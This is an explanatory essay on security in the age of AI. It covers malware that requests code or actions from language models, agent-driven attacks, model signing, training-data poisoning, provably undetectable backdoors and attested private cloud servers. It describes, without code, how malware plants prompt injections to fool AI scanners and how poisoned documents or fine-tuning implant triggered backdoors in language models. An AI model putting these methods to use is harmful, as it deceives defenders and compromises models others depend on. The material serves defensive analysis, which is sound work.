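| The request | In the file | Developers ask for such code |
| The model | On Google's servers | Many legitimate programs use it |
| The compiler | On the victim's computer | It comes with .NET |
| The generated code | Nowhere | It resembles an updater and isn't saved as a program |
| The final malware | On a file-hosting service | It isn't on the computer yet |

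Windows can pass .NET code to a scanner as the code loads, through the interface PowerShell uses, but the scanner might again find only an updater. Only the last part is harmful by itself.

Requesting code from a model, compiling it and running it straight away are more suspicious together than separately, so a scanner could have a heuristic for small programs that do all three. But a coding agent's harness also fits this description, and the agent on the accounts mailbox does much the same with shell commands. A rule that caught every program like HONESTCUE would flag a lot of legitimate software, unless the scanner also took into account who had published the program and how many other people used it.

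Google saw no sign that HONESTCUE was widely used. A single account had submitted the samples to VirusTotal, and they differed in small ways, so Google suspected that one person or a small group was still testing the idea. HONESTCUE is good evidence that such malware can be built, but not that it has harmed many people.

### Using the victim's own AI tools

QUIETVAULT steals credentials for GitHub and npm, then uses AI command-line tools already installed on the victim's computer to search for other secrets, and uploads what it finds to a public page on GitHub. Google Threat Intelligence Group observed it in real attacks. Living off the land means attacking with software already on the victim's machine, and QUIETVAULT does this with an AI agent, so it doesn't need a key or a model of its own. The victim's company may have approved the tool, and searching through files is a normal use of it.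 If the tool runs under the victim's account, its provider receives the request from a paying customer.

PROMPTSPY, an Android backdoor that the security company ESET first identified, requests actions from a language model instead of code. The May issue of Google Threat Intelligence Group's *GTIG AI Threat Tracker* (2026) explains that the malware sends Gemini a goal and a description of what is on the screen. Gemini replies with an action, such as a tap or a swipe, and its position, and the malware performs the action. In one known use, this kept the malware pinned in the phone's list of recent apps.

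As with the expenses app, the model chooses from functions already in the file. A scanner can find the code for tapping and swiping, but apps for people with disabilities use the same Android feature. The main stored request doesn't include the goal either, and Google believes the developers separated the two so they could use the malware for different purposes.

### Twelve sightings among 405 samples

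In *The State of AI-Enabled Malware August 2026* (2026), Unit 42, the research team of the security software company Palo Alto Networks, tried to measure how much of this malware reaches real computers. The team collected 405 malicious files with some connection to AI and searched for their hashes in records from the company's customers' computers. Only 12 of the files appeared in those records, and the company's products had blocked all of them.

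Most of the other samples were demonstrations by researchers, files that companies used to test their own defences, or conventional malware with the name of an AI product attached. Some of the ransomware demonstrations demanded payment to a Bitcoin address from which nobody could recover the money. Unit 42 concluded that AI "changes how the code is authored, not how it executes", and that existing methods were enough to detect the resulting code.

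That conclusion fits the 12 files well. Most were versions of FunkSec, ransomware that its developers probably wrote with a model's help. (The text counts seven versions, but the accompanying list has eight, which makes the total 12.) The remaining four were a fake recipe app, a fake Dropbox installer, a program that steals passwords and other data, and a library disguised as part of a Chinese antivirus product. Unit 42 doesn't describe any of the 12 as requesting code from a model while running. The count is therefore good news about malware that a model helped to write or advertise, but it is little evidence about malware like HONESTCUE.

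The dates support the same conclusion. The records from customers' computers end in June 2025, the month Google identified PROMPTFLUX and PROMPTSTEAL, and three months before it saw HONESTCUE. Searching by hash would also miss a program that rewrote itself on each computer, because its new hash wouldn't be on the list, and it would miss malware that nobody had yet recognised.

Twelve files are also too few to establish a detection rate. If a product misses a share $m$ of such malware, and the files are independent, the chance that it catches all 12 is $(1-m)^{12}$. A product that missed one file in ten would still have a perfect record more than a quarter of the time:

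$$(1-0.1)^{12} \approx 0.28.$$

The evidence is even weaker because the FunkSec versions shared a codebase and so weren't independent. A few files can still mean many attacks, since the recipe app alone reached more than 50 organisations.

The recipe app also shows how different checks work together. Its valid signature, from a company called Global Tech Allies, at first made the file look less suspicious in the static scan. The product then took into account that the customer's other computers rarely ran software from this signer, and that the file's entropy was 0.99997 out of a maximum of 1. A sandbox run provided the deciding evidence. Unit 42 attributes the second step to "behavioral analytics", but both clues concern the file and its publisher, so static checks still contributed, even if they couldn't decide the case alone.

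### Attacks run by agents in late 2026

Two days after publishing its count, Unit 42 warned that attacks using AI agents had begun and that organisations weren't prepared (Kapko, 2026, *Unit 42 warns AI has shifted balance of power*). The warning and the count are compatible because the count's data was more than a year old by then.

*UK cyber agency seeing ‘marked rise’ in AI-driven attacks* (Martin, 2026) reports that the UK's National Cyber Security Centre saw "a marked rise" in AI-assisted attacks from September 2026. Many of the attackers used frameworks that security testers had built to let agents look for weaknesses in a network. The agency found nothing new in the weaknesses they exploited, and the agents used tools that a typical attacker could already get. The agents were faster, cheaper and more persistent, which leaves less room for error at organisations that neglect basic precautions.

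In *The impact of AI on cyber threat* (2026), part of its annual review, the NCSC judges that AI is unlikely to change what attackers want but highly likely to make them faster and more efficient. Constantin (2026) reports in *NCSC annual review* that the agency also expects AI malware to hit British infrastructure by 2028.

The November issue of Google Threat Intelligence Group's *GTIG AI Threat Tracker* (2026) describes attackers moving from simple prompts to teams of agents. Markovic's *Google finds AI agent writing and launching exploits* (2026) summarises its main case, a system that Google found on an attacker's exposed server. When the maker of a popular web application announced a security patch, the system compared the code before and after the patch, looked for the flaw it repaired, and wrote and launched an attack on that flaw, all without human involvement. The system could use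 several models, including some that ran locally.

In attacks like this, the model and its instructions stay on the attacker's side, so the victim's antivirus software never receives a file containing a request to the model. The attacker may plant a webshell, a script for running further commands, on a web server, and the antivirus software can scan it like any other file. The remaining evidence is network traffic and commands, which are plentiful for now because these systems sacrifice stealth for speed. Dekel and Fakterman (2026), in *Recent Trends and Tactics of Agentic AI Attacks*, likewise found that attackers' agents used standard tools and left distinctive traces. Google expects these systems to become stealthier.

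### Scanners that use a model to read code

Defenders also use language models to scan for malware automatically. They give the model a script, or a readable reconstruction of a compiled program, and ask what the code does and whether it looks harmful. Unlike a pattern search, this method can work on code that resembles no earlier malware, and the model can explain its answer to an analyst.

Language models can be good at spotting conflicts between a program's purpose and its behavior. In May 2026, Google Threat Intelligence Group reported an attack, probably developed with a model's help, that bypassed the second login step of a popular administration tool. The flaw was an exception a developer had written into the login rules. Conventional tools detect crashes and unsafe handling of data, so they tend to miss errors like this. Google argues that a model can find such errors by comparing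 a rule with its exceptions. The same ability should help a scanner flag an "image generator" that copies someone's documents.

A scanner that works out what a program achieves may also help against padding. CANFAIL and LONGSTREAM, two malware families used against Ukrainian organisations, contain large amounts of harmless code that a model wrote as camouflage. LONGSTREAM checks 32 times whether daylight saving time is in force, and CANFAIL has comments, apparently written by the model, that identify unused blocks of code. Such padding could lower the score from a classifier that counts ordinary-looking features, but a scanner that looks at what the program achieves can ignore it.

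These scanners are vulnerable to prompt injection. The malware's author controls the text that the model reads, and can add sentences that tell the model the file is safe or try to distract it from the analysis. The processor never executes these sentences, so they don't affect how the malware runs. Google Threat Intelligence Group has seen real attacks use FRUITSHELL, a PowerShell program that contains such text and gives an attacker remote control of a computer. Researchers at Cisco Talos and ESET also reported on such text in 2026.

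A conventional scanner isn't affected by the planted text and can use it as a signature, since ordinary programs have little reason to address a malware analyst's AI. The vendor can also allow the model to add suspicion but not to clear a file that another check has flagged. A successful injection then only removes the model's contribution, but the model can no longer correct other scanners' false alarms.

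Even a model that isn't misled by the planted text can't analyze code that doesn't exist yet. From HONESTCUE's file, it could at most determine that the program will run whatever Gemini returns. That warning is more useful than a pattern search that finds nothing, but it also applies to many legitimate agents.

### Watching behaviour and cutting off the model

HONESTCUE shows the gap in file checks most clearly, but monitoring what the computer does gives defenders more evidence. A model wrote PROMPTSTEAL's commands, but they still had to gather system details, copy documents into one folder and send them to an outside server. A security product can watch for that sequence however the commands are worded, and the sequence is unusual for a program posing as an image generator.

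Monitoring can fail too, as Barr-Smith and colleagues found when they changed the payloads in their tests. QUIETVAULT's behaviour is harder to pick out than PROMPTSTEAL's because a coding agent routinely searches through files for its user. Uploading passwords to a public page is a better clue than the search, but by then the product has very little time to stop the upload.

The model's provider has evidence that the victim's computer lacks, because it receives the requests, generates the replies, and can compare requests from many computers. A single HONESTCUE request looks harmless, but the same request from hundreds of unrelated computers using the same key would look much less so. Attackers can also reveal details of their operations in their requests. An Iranian group asked Gemini for help with a script that contained the address of its control server and its encryption key, which helped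 Google disrupt the group's campaign.

Google disabled the accounts and other resources behind PROMPTFLUX and PROMPTSPY, and used what it had learned to improve Gemini's safeguards. If malware depends on a single stored key, disabling that key cuts off new code to every infected computer at once. SecurityBrief US reports that Google took similar action against several campaigns described in its September 2026 report. In one intrusion in that report, the attacker used a stolen credential to enter a company's cloud account and turn on AI services there, so the attacker reached the models through the victim's own account.

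Attackers can get around these controls in several ways. PROMPTSPY's operators can send it a new key remotely, and PROMPTSTEAL probably used stolen keys. The NCSC mentions both illegal resellers of access to commercial models and cheap open models. Anyone can download an open model and run it on their own hardware, where no provider can read the requests or close an account.

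## Signing a model's weights

Users download an open model as a folder of files, often from a hub such as Hugging Face, where anyone can publish. The weights take up most of the space, sometimes hundreds of gigabytes. These files exist before the model runs, so a publisher can sign them and a user can check them like any other download.

The Open Source Security Foundation (OpenSSF), an industry group, released version 1.0 of its model signing software in April 2025. Maruseac, Sablotny and colleagues (2025), in *Launch of Model Signing v1.0*, explain that one team usually trains a model and another deploys it, and that nothing on a model hub showed whether an uploaded model was the one its developers had trained.

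### Three files and one altered byte

The software signs all of a model's files together:

1. The publisher's computer calculates a hash of every file.
2. It lists the file names and hashes in a manifest.
3. The publisher signs the manifest and releases it, with the signature, as a small separate file.
4. Before loading the model, the user's computer checks the signature, hashes the downloaded files and compares the results with the manifest.

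Suppose a model has three files, and someone alters one byte of the weights before they reach the user. With invented and shortened hashes, the comparison looks like this:

| File | Hash in the signed manifest | Hash of the download |
|---|---|---|
| `config.json` | `41c7…` | `41c7…` |
| `tokenizer.json` | `b90e…` | `b90e…` |
| `model.safetensors` | `7d23…` | `e856…` |

The manifest's signature is valid, but the third hash doesn't match, so verification fails. If the attacker edits the manifest to match the altered file, the signature fails instead. The attacker could still sign a new manifest with a different key, so the user has to specify whose signature to accept. IBM's *Signature verification*, a guide for users of its Granite models, gives the exact IBM identity to enter.

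Signature verification fails if any byte of the weights has changed, but it can't show how much the change matters. Suppose a weight of 0.03125 is stored as a standard 16-bit floating-point number. Flipping its lowest bit changes it to about 0.03128, which nobody would notice. Flipping the highest bit of its exponent changes it to 2,048, which could ruin the model's output.

The manifest protects only the files it lists. *Conjunctive Poisoning in AI Supply-Chain Applications* (2026) describes an attack through the templates that arrange text for a model. Publishers often leave these templates unsigned because developers keep editing them. Signing the whole release and checking all of it when the model runs prevents the attack. The OpenSSF format can cover settings files and tokenizers (which split text into units for the model) as well as weights.

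### Who signs and who checks

NVIDIA has signed all the models it publishes in its NGC catalogue since March 2025, according to its *Bringing Verifiable Trust to AI Models*. IBM signs every version of Granite 4.0 that it puts on Hugging Face, although its guide still calls signing experimental. HiddenLayer, a security company that helped write the OpenSSF format, reported that Google was testing signatures on its Kaggle model hub.

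Fewer systems check the signatures automatically. NVIDIA's NIM, a package for running models, compares checksums of the files it downloads, which can reveal a damaged file. But NVIDIA's *Model Signature Verification* describes the signature check as a separate procedure, in which the user downloads the signature and a certificate and runs a command.

Kliukovkin (2026), in *Cold-Start Model Delivery in Kubernetes Inference Serving*, found that enforcement when a model goes into service "remains manual". He proposed an automatic check for KServe, a widely used system for running models on clusters of computers, but KServe's developers hadn't adopted it by July 2026. In his measurements, hashing a model during the download added less than 0.1% to the delivery time, so speed is a poor reason to leave the check out, though a separate pass afterwards added up to 53%. His design checks the files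 only once, so a malicious program with access to the same storage could still change them later.

### Model files that run code

Some model files can run malicious code as soon as someone opens them. Pickle, Python's standard format for saving objects, stores instructions for rebuilding each object. Those instructions can call almost any function available to Python, including one that runs shell commands. For years, models made with PyTorch, a popular machine-learning library, usually came as pickle files, so loading a stranger's model could run any code the stranger had put in it. Google (2025) describes models as collections of weights, "sometimes also with arbitrary code".

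The safetensors format removes this risk by leaving out the instructions. A file starts with a short header that gives the name, number type, shape and position of each block of weights, and the rest is numbers. The loader only has to copy them into memory.

The old checks work well here because the dangerous code is in the file. A scanner can search a pickle file for suspicious function calls without loading it, and a company can refuse every format except safetensors. Since 2025, PyTorch's loader has by default accepted only a short list of approved operations in pickle files. Some models also come with Python scripts, which a company can review and sign like other software.

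### Two hundred and fifty poisoned documents

A correctly signed safetensors file can still contain a backdoor, a hidden behaviour that appears only when the input includes a particular trigger. The publisher may not know about it, since developers train language models on huge amounts of text from the web, where an attacker can post documents.

*Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-constant Number of Poison Samples* (Souly, Rando and colleagues, 2025) reports an experiment on how many documents an attacker would need to poison a model. The researchers, from Anthropic, the UK AI Security Institute and the Alan Turing Institute, trained 72 models from scratch, ranging from 600 million to 13 billion weights. Each poisoned document consisted of ordinary text, a trigger phrase and random words. If the attack worked, the model wrote gibberish after the trigger and normal text otherwise.

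At every size, 250 documents were enough, but 100 were not. Earlier studies had assumed that an attacker needed a fixed share of the training data, which would make large models hard to poison. The largest models here trained on over 20 times as much clean text as the smallest, and the same number of documents still worked. The documents averaged 1,680 tokens (words or parts of words), so for the largest models the poisoned share was

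$$\frac{250 \times 1{,}680}{260 \text{ billion}} \approx 0.00016\%.$$

Gibberish is an easy behaviour to plant. Souly and colleagues also didn't test whether the backdoor would survive the later training that turns a raw model into a safe assistant. In a smaller experiment, further training on clean text slowly weakened a backdoor that made a model switch from English to German. In *Agentic Backdoors via Pretraining Poisoning*, Hu, Hu and colleagues (2026) later found that planted behaviour could survive further training on clean text, especially in the larger of their models. They varied the poisoned share of the data, so they didn't test whether a fixed number of documents is enough.

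A publisher could sign such a model in good faith, and the signature would be valid because the attacker acted before the weights were finished.

### The theorem on undetectable backdoors

*Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models* (Goldwasser, Kim and colleagues, 2022) proves that buyers of some models cannot find a backdoor by studying the weights, provided that certain mathematical problems are as hard as cryptographers believe.

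In their example, a bank pays a contractor to train a model that approves or refuses loans. The contractor delivers a backdoored model $\tilde h$ and keeps a secret key $k$. With the key, the contractor can make a slight change to any application that reverses the decision. Let $h$ be an honestly trained model. The backdoor is undetectable if every efficient test $T$ gives the answer "backdoored" almost equally often for both:

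$$\left|\Pr[T(\tilde h)=1]-\Pr[T(h)=1]\right| \approx 0.$$

A test is "efficient" if its running time grows no faster than some fixed power of the model's size. As the model grows, the difference has to shrink so fast that it is useless in practice.

Goldwasser and colleagues prove this in two settings. In the first, the bank can only submit applications and see the decisions. The contractor can then backdoor any model by adding a hidden check for a digital signature in the application's least important digits. The bank would have to forge a signature to find an application that triggers the backdoor. The proof assumes only that secure digital signatures exist. However, someone who examined the weights might notice the added check.

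The second setting gives the bank all the weights and the training data, and the proof covers only simple networks. One type computes many features of the form $\cos(2\pi(g\cdot x+b))$, where $x$ is the application and $g$ and $b$ are random. Training decides only how much each feature counts. The contractor chooses each $g$ so that it looks random but $g\cdot k$ is very close to a whole number plus one half. Adding the key to an application then shifts every cosine by half a turn:

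$$\cos(2\pi(g\cdot(x+k)+b)) \approx -\cos(2\pi(g\cdot x+b)).$$

Every feature changes sign, so their weighted sum does too, and a refusal becomes an approval. Telling these values of $g$ from random ones would require solving Continuous Learning With Errors, a problem related to the lattice problems behind some modern encryption. For a second network type, the assumption is instead that a statistical problem called Sparse PCA is hard.

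The contractor uses the agreed data and training program and tampers only with the random numbers. A signed record of the data and the program would be accurate but would not reveal the backdoor. The bank could supply the random numbers itself and demand proof that the contractor used them, but this is much harder to arrange if the bank also relies on the contractor to design the training.

Cohen's proof ruled out only a perfect virus detector. This theorem rules out even a mediocre backdoor detector, though only for particular backdoors and under unproven assumptions.

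### What later work changed

Several papers in 2026 tested or extended the theorem. In *Implementing a White-Box Undetectable Backdoor for Random Fourier Features*, Collins, Cumberland and colleagues (2026) built the cosine version with ordinary scientific software. They ran statistical tests and found no evidence of a detectable difference between the backdoored models and clean ones.

Bogdanov, Rosen and Vafa (2026), in *Statistically Undetectable Backdoors in Deep Neural Networks*, pointed out that in that version an outsider without the key can efficiently find changes that work even better than the contractor's, so the backdoor is well hidden but gives its owner no advantage. Their own construction does give the owner an advantage, in deep networks whose first layer is a fixed random matrix. The key lets the owner make the network treat two different inputs as almost identical. Apart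 from a small error, no test can distinguish the backdoored model from one without a backdoor, however much computing power it uses.

*Undetectable Backdoors in Model Parameters* (Choudhary, Patlan and colleagues, 2026) extends the result to kinds of image classifier already in use, again assuming that Sparse PCA is hard. Other researchers have a method that covers some language models, but Bogdanov and colleagues consider it far from practical. The theorem is therefore a reason not to rely on inspection, but it is not evidence that today's agents contain such backdoors.

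Poisoning gives an attacker less protection. Kaneko (2026), in *Poisoning-Based Backdoors Are Not Cryptographic*, considered attackers who can pass information about the trigger to the model only through the labels on training examples. If training can teach the model to recognise the trigger, a defender with as many labelled examples can learn to recognise it by running the same training. This could help investigators who have collected examples after an attack, but not a defender who has never seen the trigger.

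Goldwasser and colleagues suggested looking for ways to neutralise backdoors without finding them, for example by adding random noise to each input. Noise works only if it is large enough for the particular backdoor, and an attacker who knows the defence can prepare for it. *Oblivious Defense in ML Models* (2024) continues the search for ways to remove backdoors without detecting them.

### Compressed and retrained copies

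Many people who run an open model on their own computers use a quantised copy rather than the weights that the publisher signed. Someone else has usually made the copy, which always has a new hash and might store each weight in about four bits instead of 16.

In principle, a user could repeat the compression and compare the results. Liu and Tsai (2026), in *What You Sign Is Not What You Run*, examined 198 of the most downloaded collections of compressed models on Hugging Face and found that none recorded enough about how its files were made for others to repeat the process reliably. But when they supplied two missing details for four collections that disclosed more than most, they recreated seven of eight files exactly on a machine with an ordinary PC processor.

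One of those details was a compiler setting that controls whether the computer rounds once or twice when it calculates $a \times b + c$. The slight difference in the result can change the scale that the program chooses for a block of weights, and therefore the stored bytes. Liu and Tsai measured one model's perplexity, which is lower when a model predicts text better, and got 10.744 with one setting and 10.750 with the other. That difference is too small to distinguish from chance. An allowlist would treat the two files as unrelated, although by this measure they were practically the same model.

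The maker of a compressed copy can sign it, but that signature doesn't prove that the copy came from the original weights. Even a copy made honestly from those weights may behave differently, because an attacker can prepare weights that become harmful only when compressed. Tests of the original would then miss the harmful behavior.

Fine-tuning, a short round of extra training for a particular job, causes the same difficulty. It may change little beyond the model's tone, or it may add a backdoor. Souly and colleagues fine-tuned a Llama model with poisoned examples so that it complied with harmful requests when a trigger was present. The attack's success depended mainly on the number of poisoned examples, even when the number of clean examples grew from 1,000 to 100,000.

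Software patches also change hashes, but a reviewer can read the lines that a programmer changed. Comparing two sets of weights gives billions of small numerical differences that nobody can read like that. Some fine-tuning leaves the original weights unchanged and stores the changes in a small extra file. *Scalable GPU-Based Integrity Verification for Large Machine Learning Models* (2025) calls for measuring both the weights and the extra file and binding the measurements together. A user can then confirm which original weights and which changes are present, but still has to test the combination.

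### Test results for exact weights

Signing makes behavioural tests more useful. A laboratory can spend weeks testing a model, put the manifest's hash in its report and sign the report. Anyone whose files match that hash knows the results apply to their weights and doesn't have to repeat the tests. If researchers later find a backdoor, users can check the hash to see whether they have the affected model. Without the hash, a report on "Granite 4.0" could refer to any of several versions.

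Standards for such records are still developing. The Coalition for Secure AI (CoSAI), an industry group, approved its plan for tamper-proof records about models, *Signing ML Artifacts* (2025). IBM Research's *Toward a transparent supply chain for AI* describes a machine-readable record that would list a model's datasets, weights, earlier versions and evaluation results. The OpenSSF format has an optional section for extra information, but *An Introduction to the OpenSSF Model Signing (OMS) Specification* (Maruseac, Wickens and colleagues, 2025) listed support for it as future work.

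A reusable report is still only as good as its tests. Suppose a model handles 3,000 randomly chosen emails without a harmful action. If its true failure rate were 0.1%, it would have about a 5% chance of doing so:

$$(1-0.001)^{3000} \approx 0.05.$$

The laboratory can therefore be fairly confident that the rate is below 0.1% for similar emails. The tests provide little evidence about an email written by an attacker, or one containing a trigger the laboratory never tried. The result also depends on the system prompt and the tools, so the report has to record those. A company that changes them needs new tests, even though the weights have the same hash.

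All of this works only if the user has the files. A customer of a hosted model can't hash the weights on the provider's server, and needs separate proof that the server is running the model the laboratory tested.

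## Apple's Private Cloud Compute and proof of what a server runs

A provider that promises not to keep its customers' requests could still start logging them after a software update, without anyone outside noticing. Apple introduced Private Cloud Compute (PCC) in June 2024 so that users would not have to rely on such a promise. PCC servers handle Apple Intelligence requests that are too demanding for an iPhone, iPad or Mac. Before sending a request, the device requires proof of what software the server is running.

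Even simple jobs can go to these servers. In *Unlocking Apple's Private Cloud Compute*, Dittmar, Stephan and colleagues (2026) tested Apple's features on a Mac and found that it proofread text on the device but used PCC to summarise an email. It chose where to run each task without telling the user.

### Measuring software at start-up

A trusted execution environment is a part of a computer that the hardware isolates, so even the machine's administrator can't read or change what is inside. Cloud companies often offer one as a confidential virtual machine, a complete virtual computer whose memory the processor encrypts. A remote customer still needs evidence of what is running inside it.

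That evidence comes from measured start-up, in which each stage of the start-up software hashes the next stage before running it. On many PCs, a security chip called a TPM combines each new hash with its record so far:

$$m_{\text{new}} = H(m_{\text{old}} \,\|\, H(\text{component})).$$

Here $H$ is the hash function and $\|$ joins two values. Software can add to the record but can't overwrite it, so a malicious program that starts late can't erase the record of how it was loaded. The chip then signs the final value with a key that never leaves the chip. wolfSSL's *TPM 2.0 Sealing Policies with wolfTPM* (2026) explains that routine updates also change the value, so a secret locked to the old value can't be unlocked after an update.

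Apple built its first PCC servers with its own chips and gave them a reduced version of the iPhone's operating system. According to Apple's *Private Cloud Compute*, a separate security processor, the Secure Enclave, loads a signed list of all the code that may run on the server. Nobody can add to the list while the server is running. The server's attestation contains measurements of its software and comes with a public key for encrypting requests.

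### A public list of releases

Apple's signature alone wouldn't protect users from Apple, because a rogue employee with access to the signing system could validly sign a version of the server software that stored every request.

Apple therefore publishes the measurements of every release in a transparency log, a public list that it can add entries to but can't remove them from without detection. Willison (2024) compares it to the logs where certificate authorities record the certificates they issue. Such a log typically has a single hash that covers all its entries. When the log grows, its operator supplies a short proof that the new version still contains everything in the old one, and anyone who kept the old hash can check the proof.

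An iPhone sends data only to a server whose measurements match a release in the log. The log can't prevent a bad release, but it makes one much harder to hide. The employee's version would have to appear in the log before any phone sent data to a server running it, and it would stay there for researchers to find.

Apple also publishes the software itself, but may take up to 90 days after the log entry to do so. A phone may therefore trust a release that no outsider has had a chance to examine.

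### One email summary

Suppose an employee reads a customer's email about the March invoices on an iPhone and asks for a summary:

1. The phone already has a supply of one-time tokens, which show that it may use PCC. Apple signs them without seeing their contents, so it can't later tell which device received a particular token.
2. A load balancer, which has no information about the user, offers the phone a small group of servers that are likely to be free.
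3. The phone checks each server's certificate and attestation, and rejects any server whose measurements aren't in the log.
4. The phone encrypts the email, the instruction and the name of the model it wants, so that only the servers that passed can decrypt them.
5. The request travels through a relay that another company runs. The relay can see the phone's internet address but can't read the request. Apple's gateway receives the request without the address and checks the token.
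6. One server decrypts the request, runs the model, returns the summary and deletes the data.

Dittmar and colleagues confirmed that Apple's devices follow this protocol, but found that the servers' checks were looser than Apple's documentation described. They could use a "one-time" token between two and five times. The servers also accepted a longer-lived token without checking its signature, although Apple's published source code contains that check. These gaps didn't expose anyone's email, and an attacker would still have needed a valid one-time token. Separately, the server that processes a request receives enough information to link it to other requests from the same device, which weakens anonymity. Apple acknowledged the findings and clarified its documentation, but did not change the protocol or the checks.

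### New code, scripts and settings

Apple's design rules out several ways of generating code that earlier cases relied on. The servers can't make new memory executable, so a JIT compiler won't work on them. They have no remote shell or debugging tools, and administrators can't load extra software during an outage.

Apple's 2024 description doesn't mention interpreters, and a ban on new machine code doesn't exclude them. Apple left out the shell, the most obvious interpreter, but researchers would have to search each release for others.

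Other instructions can arrive after start-up. ConductAtlas, a service that tracks changes to companies' documents, captured the contents list of Apple's updated security guide. The list includes settings that Apple can change while a server is running, and a component called PCC Agent that carries out workflows and coordinates tool calls.

A flaw that Apple fixed in 2026 shows that attestation can miss a server's settings. Cyber Security News' *Apple Private Cloud Compute Flaw Enables Root File Writes* reports that a researcher at Sentry Security found a way to plant files on a server's writable storage during start-up. One such file made the server send an outside machine its logs, which included the length of each prompt and which app had sent it. The attestation covered the installed software but not these files, so the altered server looked the same as a clean one. The researcher worked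 only in Apple's test environment and received $150,000. According to Apple's description in MITRE's *CVE-2026-20685* (2026), an attacker would need "a privileged network position".

Confidential virtual machines have a similar limit. Galanou, Lubitz and colleagues (2025) point out that attestation of these machines covers only what the machine measured at start-up, so it misses later changes.

### What the attestation proves

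If the chip and its keys are sound, the employee's phone can establish the following:

| Item | What the phone can establish | What remains open |
|---|---|---|
| Operating system | The server started a release that is in the public log | Undiscovered bugs, and files outside the measurements |
| Serving software | All the code on the server belongs to that release | Whether the code handles data as Apple promises |
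| Model | The server protects the model's files from alteration, as it does its code | How the model behaves |
| Answer | It came from a server that passed the checks | Whether it is correct |

The model's row offers weaker assurance than it may seem to, because Apple lets researchers run its server software on a Mac only with demonstration models. An outside laboratory therefore can't test the production weights and publish results for their exact hash, as it could with a signed open model.

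The row for the answer matters most to the employee. If the customer's email contains a hidden instruction to describe every invoice as paid, the model's summary may be false even though the server passes every check.

### Gemini-based models on Google's servers

In January 2026, Google and Apple announced that Apple would base its next models on Google's Gemini (Google, 2026). In June, Apple's *Expanding Private Cloud Compute* added that the most demanding tasks, including those in which an agent uses tools, would run in Google's data centres. According to MacTechNews' *Federighi und Co. über die enge Google-Kooperation*, Apple's software chief, Craig Federighi, said that no Gemini app code runs on the iPhone and that Apple still can't access requests.

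The new servers combine Intel processors, NVIDIA graphics chips and Google's Titan security chip. Patil and Lagar-Cavilla (2026) explain in *Powering the next era of Confidential AI* that Intel's TDX isolates the virtual machines, while NVIDIA's equivalent protects data on the graphics chips. Apple and Google also developed open-source software for the host machines so that outsiders can inspect the layer beneath the virtual machines.

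Apple's promises haven't changed, but users now depend on more companies to keep them. Apple has tried to turn this into an advantage by requiring the attestation for any component that could leak user data to rest on hardware from at least two independent vendors, so one vendor's stolen key shouldn't be enough to fake it. Apple also keeps an append-only record of every Google machine in the system, and its devices accept only software that Apple has approved. But when Apple announced the change, it said it would phase in all the protections over a summer preview, so the earliest requests didn't have all of them.

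Apple also opened its PCC model to other developers' apps in 2026. In a conference video, Apple suggested using it for features that make many tool calls. The server's attestation doesn't cover what those tools do on the phone or elsewhere.

### Google's Private AI Compute

Google runs a similar system for its own phones. *Private AI Compute* (Yagnik, 2025) announced it in November 2025 as a way to use large Gemini models in the cloud while keeping the user's data private. The models run on TPUs, Google's own AI chips. Google first used the system on the Pixel 10, where it improved an assistant's suggestions and let the Recorder app summarise transcripts in more languages.

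MacRumors' *Google Announces Its Own Version of Apple's Private Cloud Compute* (2025) reports that in Google's system, as in PCC, the phone checks the server through attestation before opening an encrypted connection, and that Google says its own engineers can't reach the data. The check establishes that the server is running software on an approved list. How much this reassures a sceptical user depends on who can see the list and examine the software, so Apple's log and published builds matter as much as its chips.

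### Chip makers, physical attacks and unread builds

All this evidence depends on a key inside a chip. If the chip's maker certified a key that it also kept outside the chip, it could imitate a genuine server and send a phone any measurements it liked. Unmitigated Risk's *A CA Built for the Threat Model We Actually Have* praises PCC for letting the user's device, rather than Apple, decide whether to accept a server. But Apple writes the software that makes this decision and also designs the chips in the original servers. PCC therefore protects users much better against an intruder or a single dishonest employee than against Apple as a whole. Apple's safeguard is an outside observer that monitors the inspection of its servers before they receive certificates, but the two-vendor rule on Google's servers is stronger.

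In 2025 researchers showed that someone with physical access to a server could extract secrets from the protected environments of current Intel and AMD processors. The chip makers replied that these environments are not designed to resist such physical attacks. Outside reviews often exclude physical attacks too. NCC Group's review of Confidential Space, a different Google product, did not cover physical access to the processor or side channels (clues such as timing that leak secrets).

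Apple does count physical attackers among the threats to PCC. It photographs the components of its own servers at high resolution before sealing them, and fits a switch that detects tampering. It also tries to make a successful attack less useful. Suppose there are 5,000 servers, the load balancer spreads requests evenly, and each phone encrypts its request to ten of them. An attacker who has broken into one server could decrypt about

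$$\frac{10}{5000} = 0.2\%$$

of requests, and couldn't choose whose. Trail of Bits' *PCC* (2024), an assessment by a security company, found this idea new in machine learning and agreed that it reduces the harm from leaky hardware. It is less comforting for the people whose requests make up the 0.2%. For the servers in Google's data centres, Apple says it doesn't rely on confidential computing alone to stop side-channel attacks and also requires the host's software to be open to inspection.

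Publishing software helps only if someone studies it. A trusted execution environment keeps outsiders away from the data, but Zhang, Priolkar and colleagues warn in *Erebor* that the service's own software inside it can still pass the data on. Apple publishes its releases as compiled programs, without the names that make such code easier to follow, and supplies source code for only some parts. Dittmar and colleagues note that researchers can't rebuild the programs from source to check that they match. Attestation identifies the compiled program, so a reassuring line in the source code may not describe what the server does, as the missing signature check showed.

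Apple responds by making inspection easier for outsiders and paying them for flaws they find. Its *Security research on Private Cloud Compute* describes tools for downloading each release, running it on a Mac and modifying it. The company offers up to $100,000 for a way to run code that the attestation doesn't cover, and up to $1 million for the most serious remote attacks. The Sentry Security finding is evidence that outsiders do look for serious flaws, but finding one doesn't show how many remain.

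### Running the request again

Someone who has a copy of the model can also check the answer itself by running the same request and comparing the results. This needs no special hardware, and it catches mistakes as well as fraud. *DiFR* (Karvonen, Reuter and colleagues, 2025) cites tests in which some companies hosting the open model Kimi K2 produced tool calls that were only 61% to 72% similar to those of a reference version.

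The difficulty is that an honest server may not give the same answer twice. Computers round the result of each addition, so the order of additions matters. With three significant digits,

$$(100 + 0.4) + 0.4 = 100, \qquad 100 + (0.4 + 0.4) = 101.$$

*Vosti* (2026) explains how this affects language models. A server processes several users' requests together, and the size of the group can change the order in which the graphics chip adds numbers. This changes the sums only slightly, but when two words are almost tied, it can change which one the model outputs, which then affects every later word. In an experiment that Karvonen and colleagues cite, 1,000 runs of the same input produced 80 different outputs, even though the model was set to always output the highest-scoring word.

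One solution is to remove the variation. *CoRun* (2026) lists serving systems that do this by calculating in an order that doesn't depend on the other requests. *EigenAI* (2026) uses exact repetition to settle disputes, because otherwise a single differing bit would make it impossible to tell honest servers from dishonest ones. This works when everyone uses the same hardware and software, which competing hosts rarely do.

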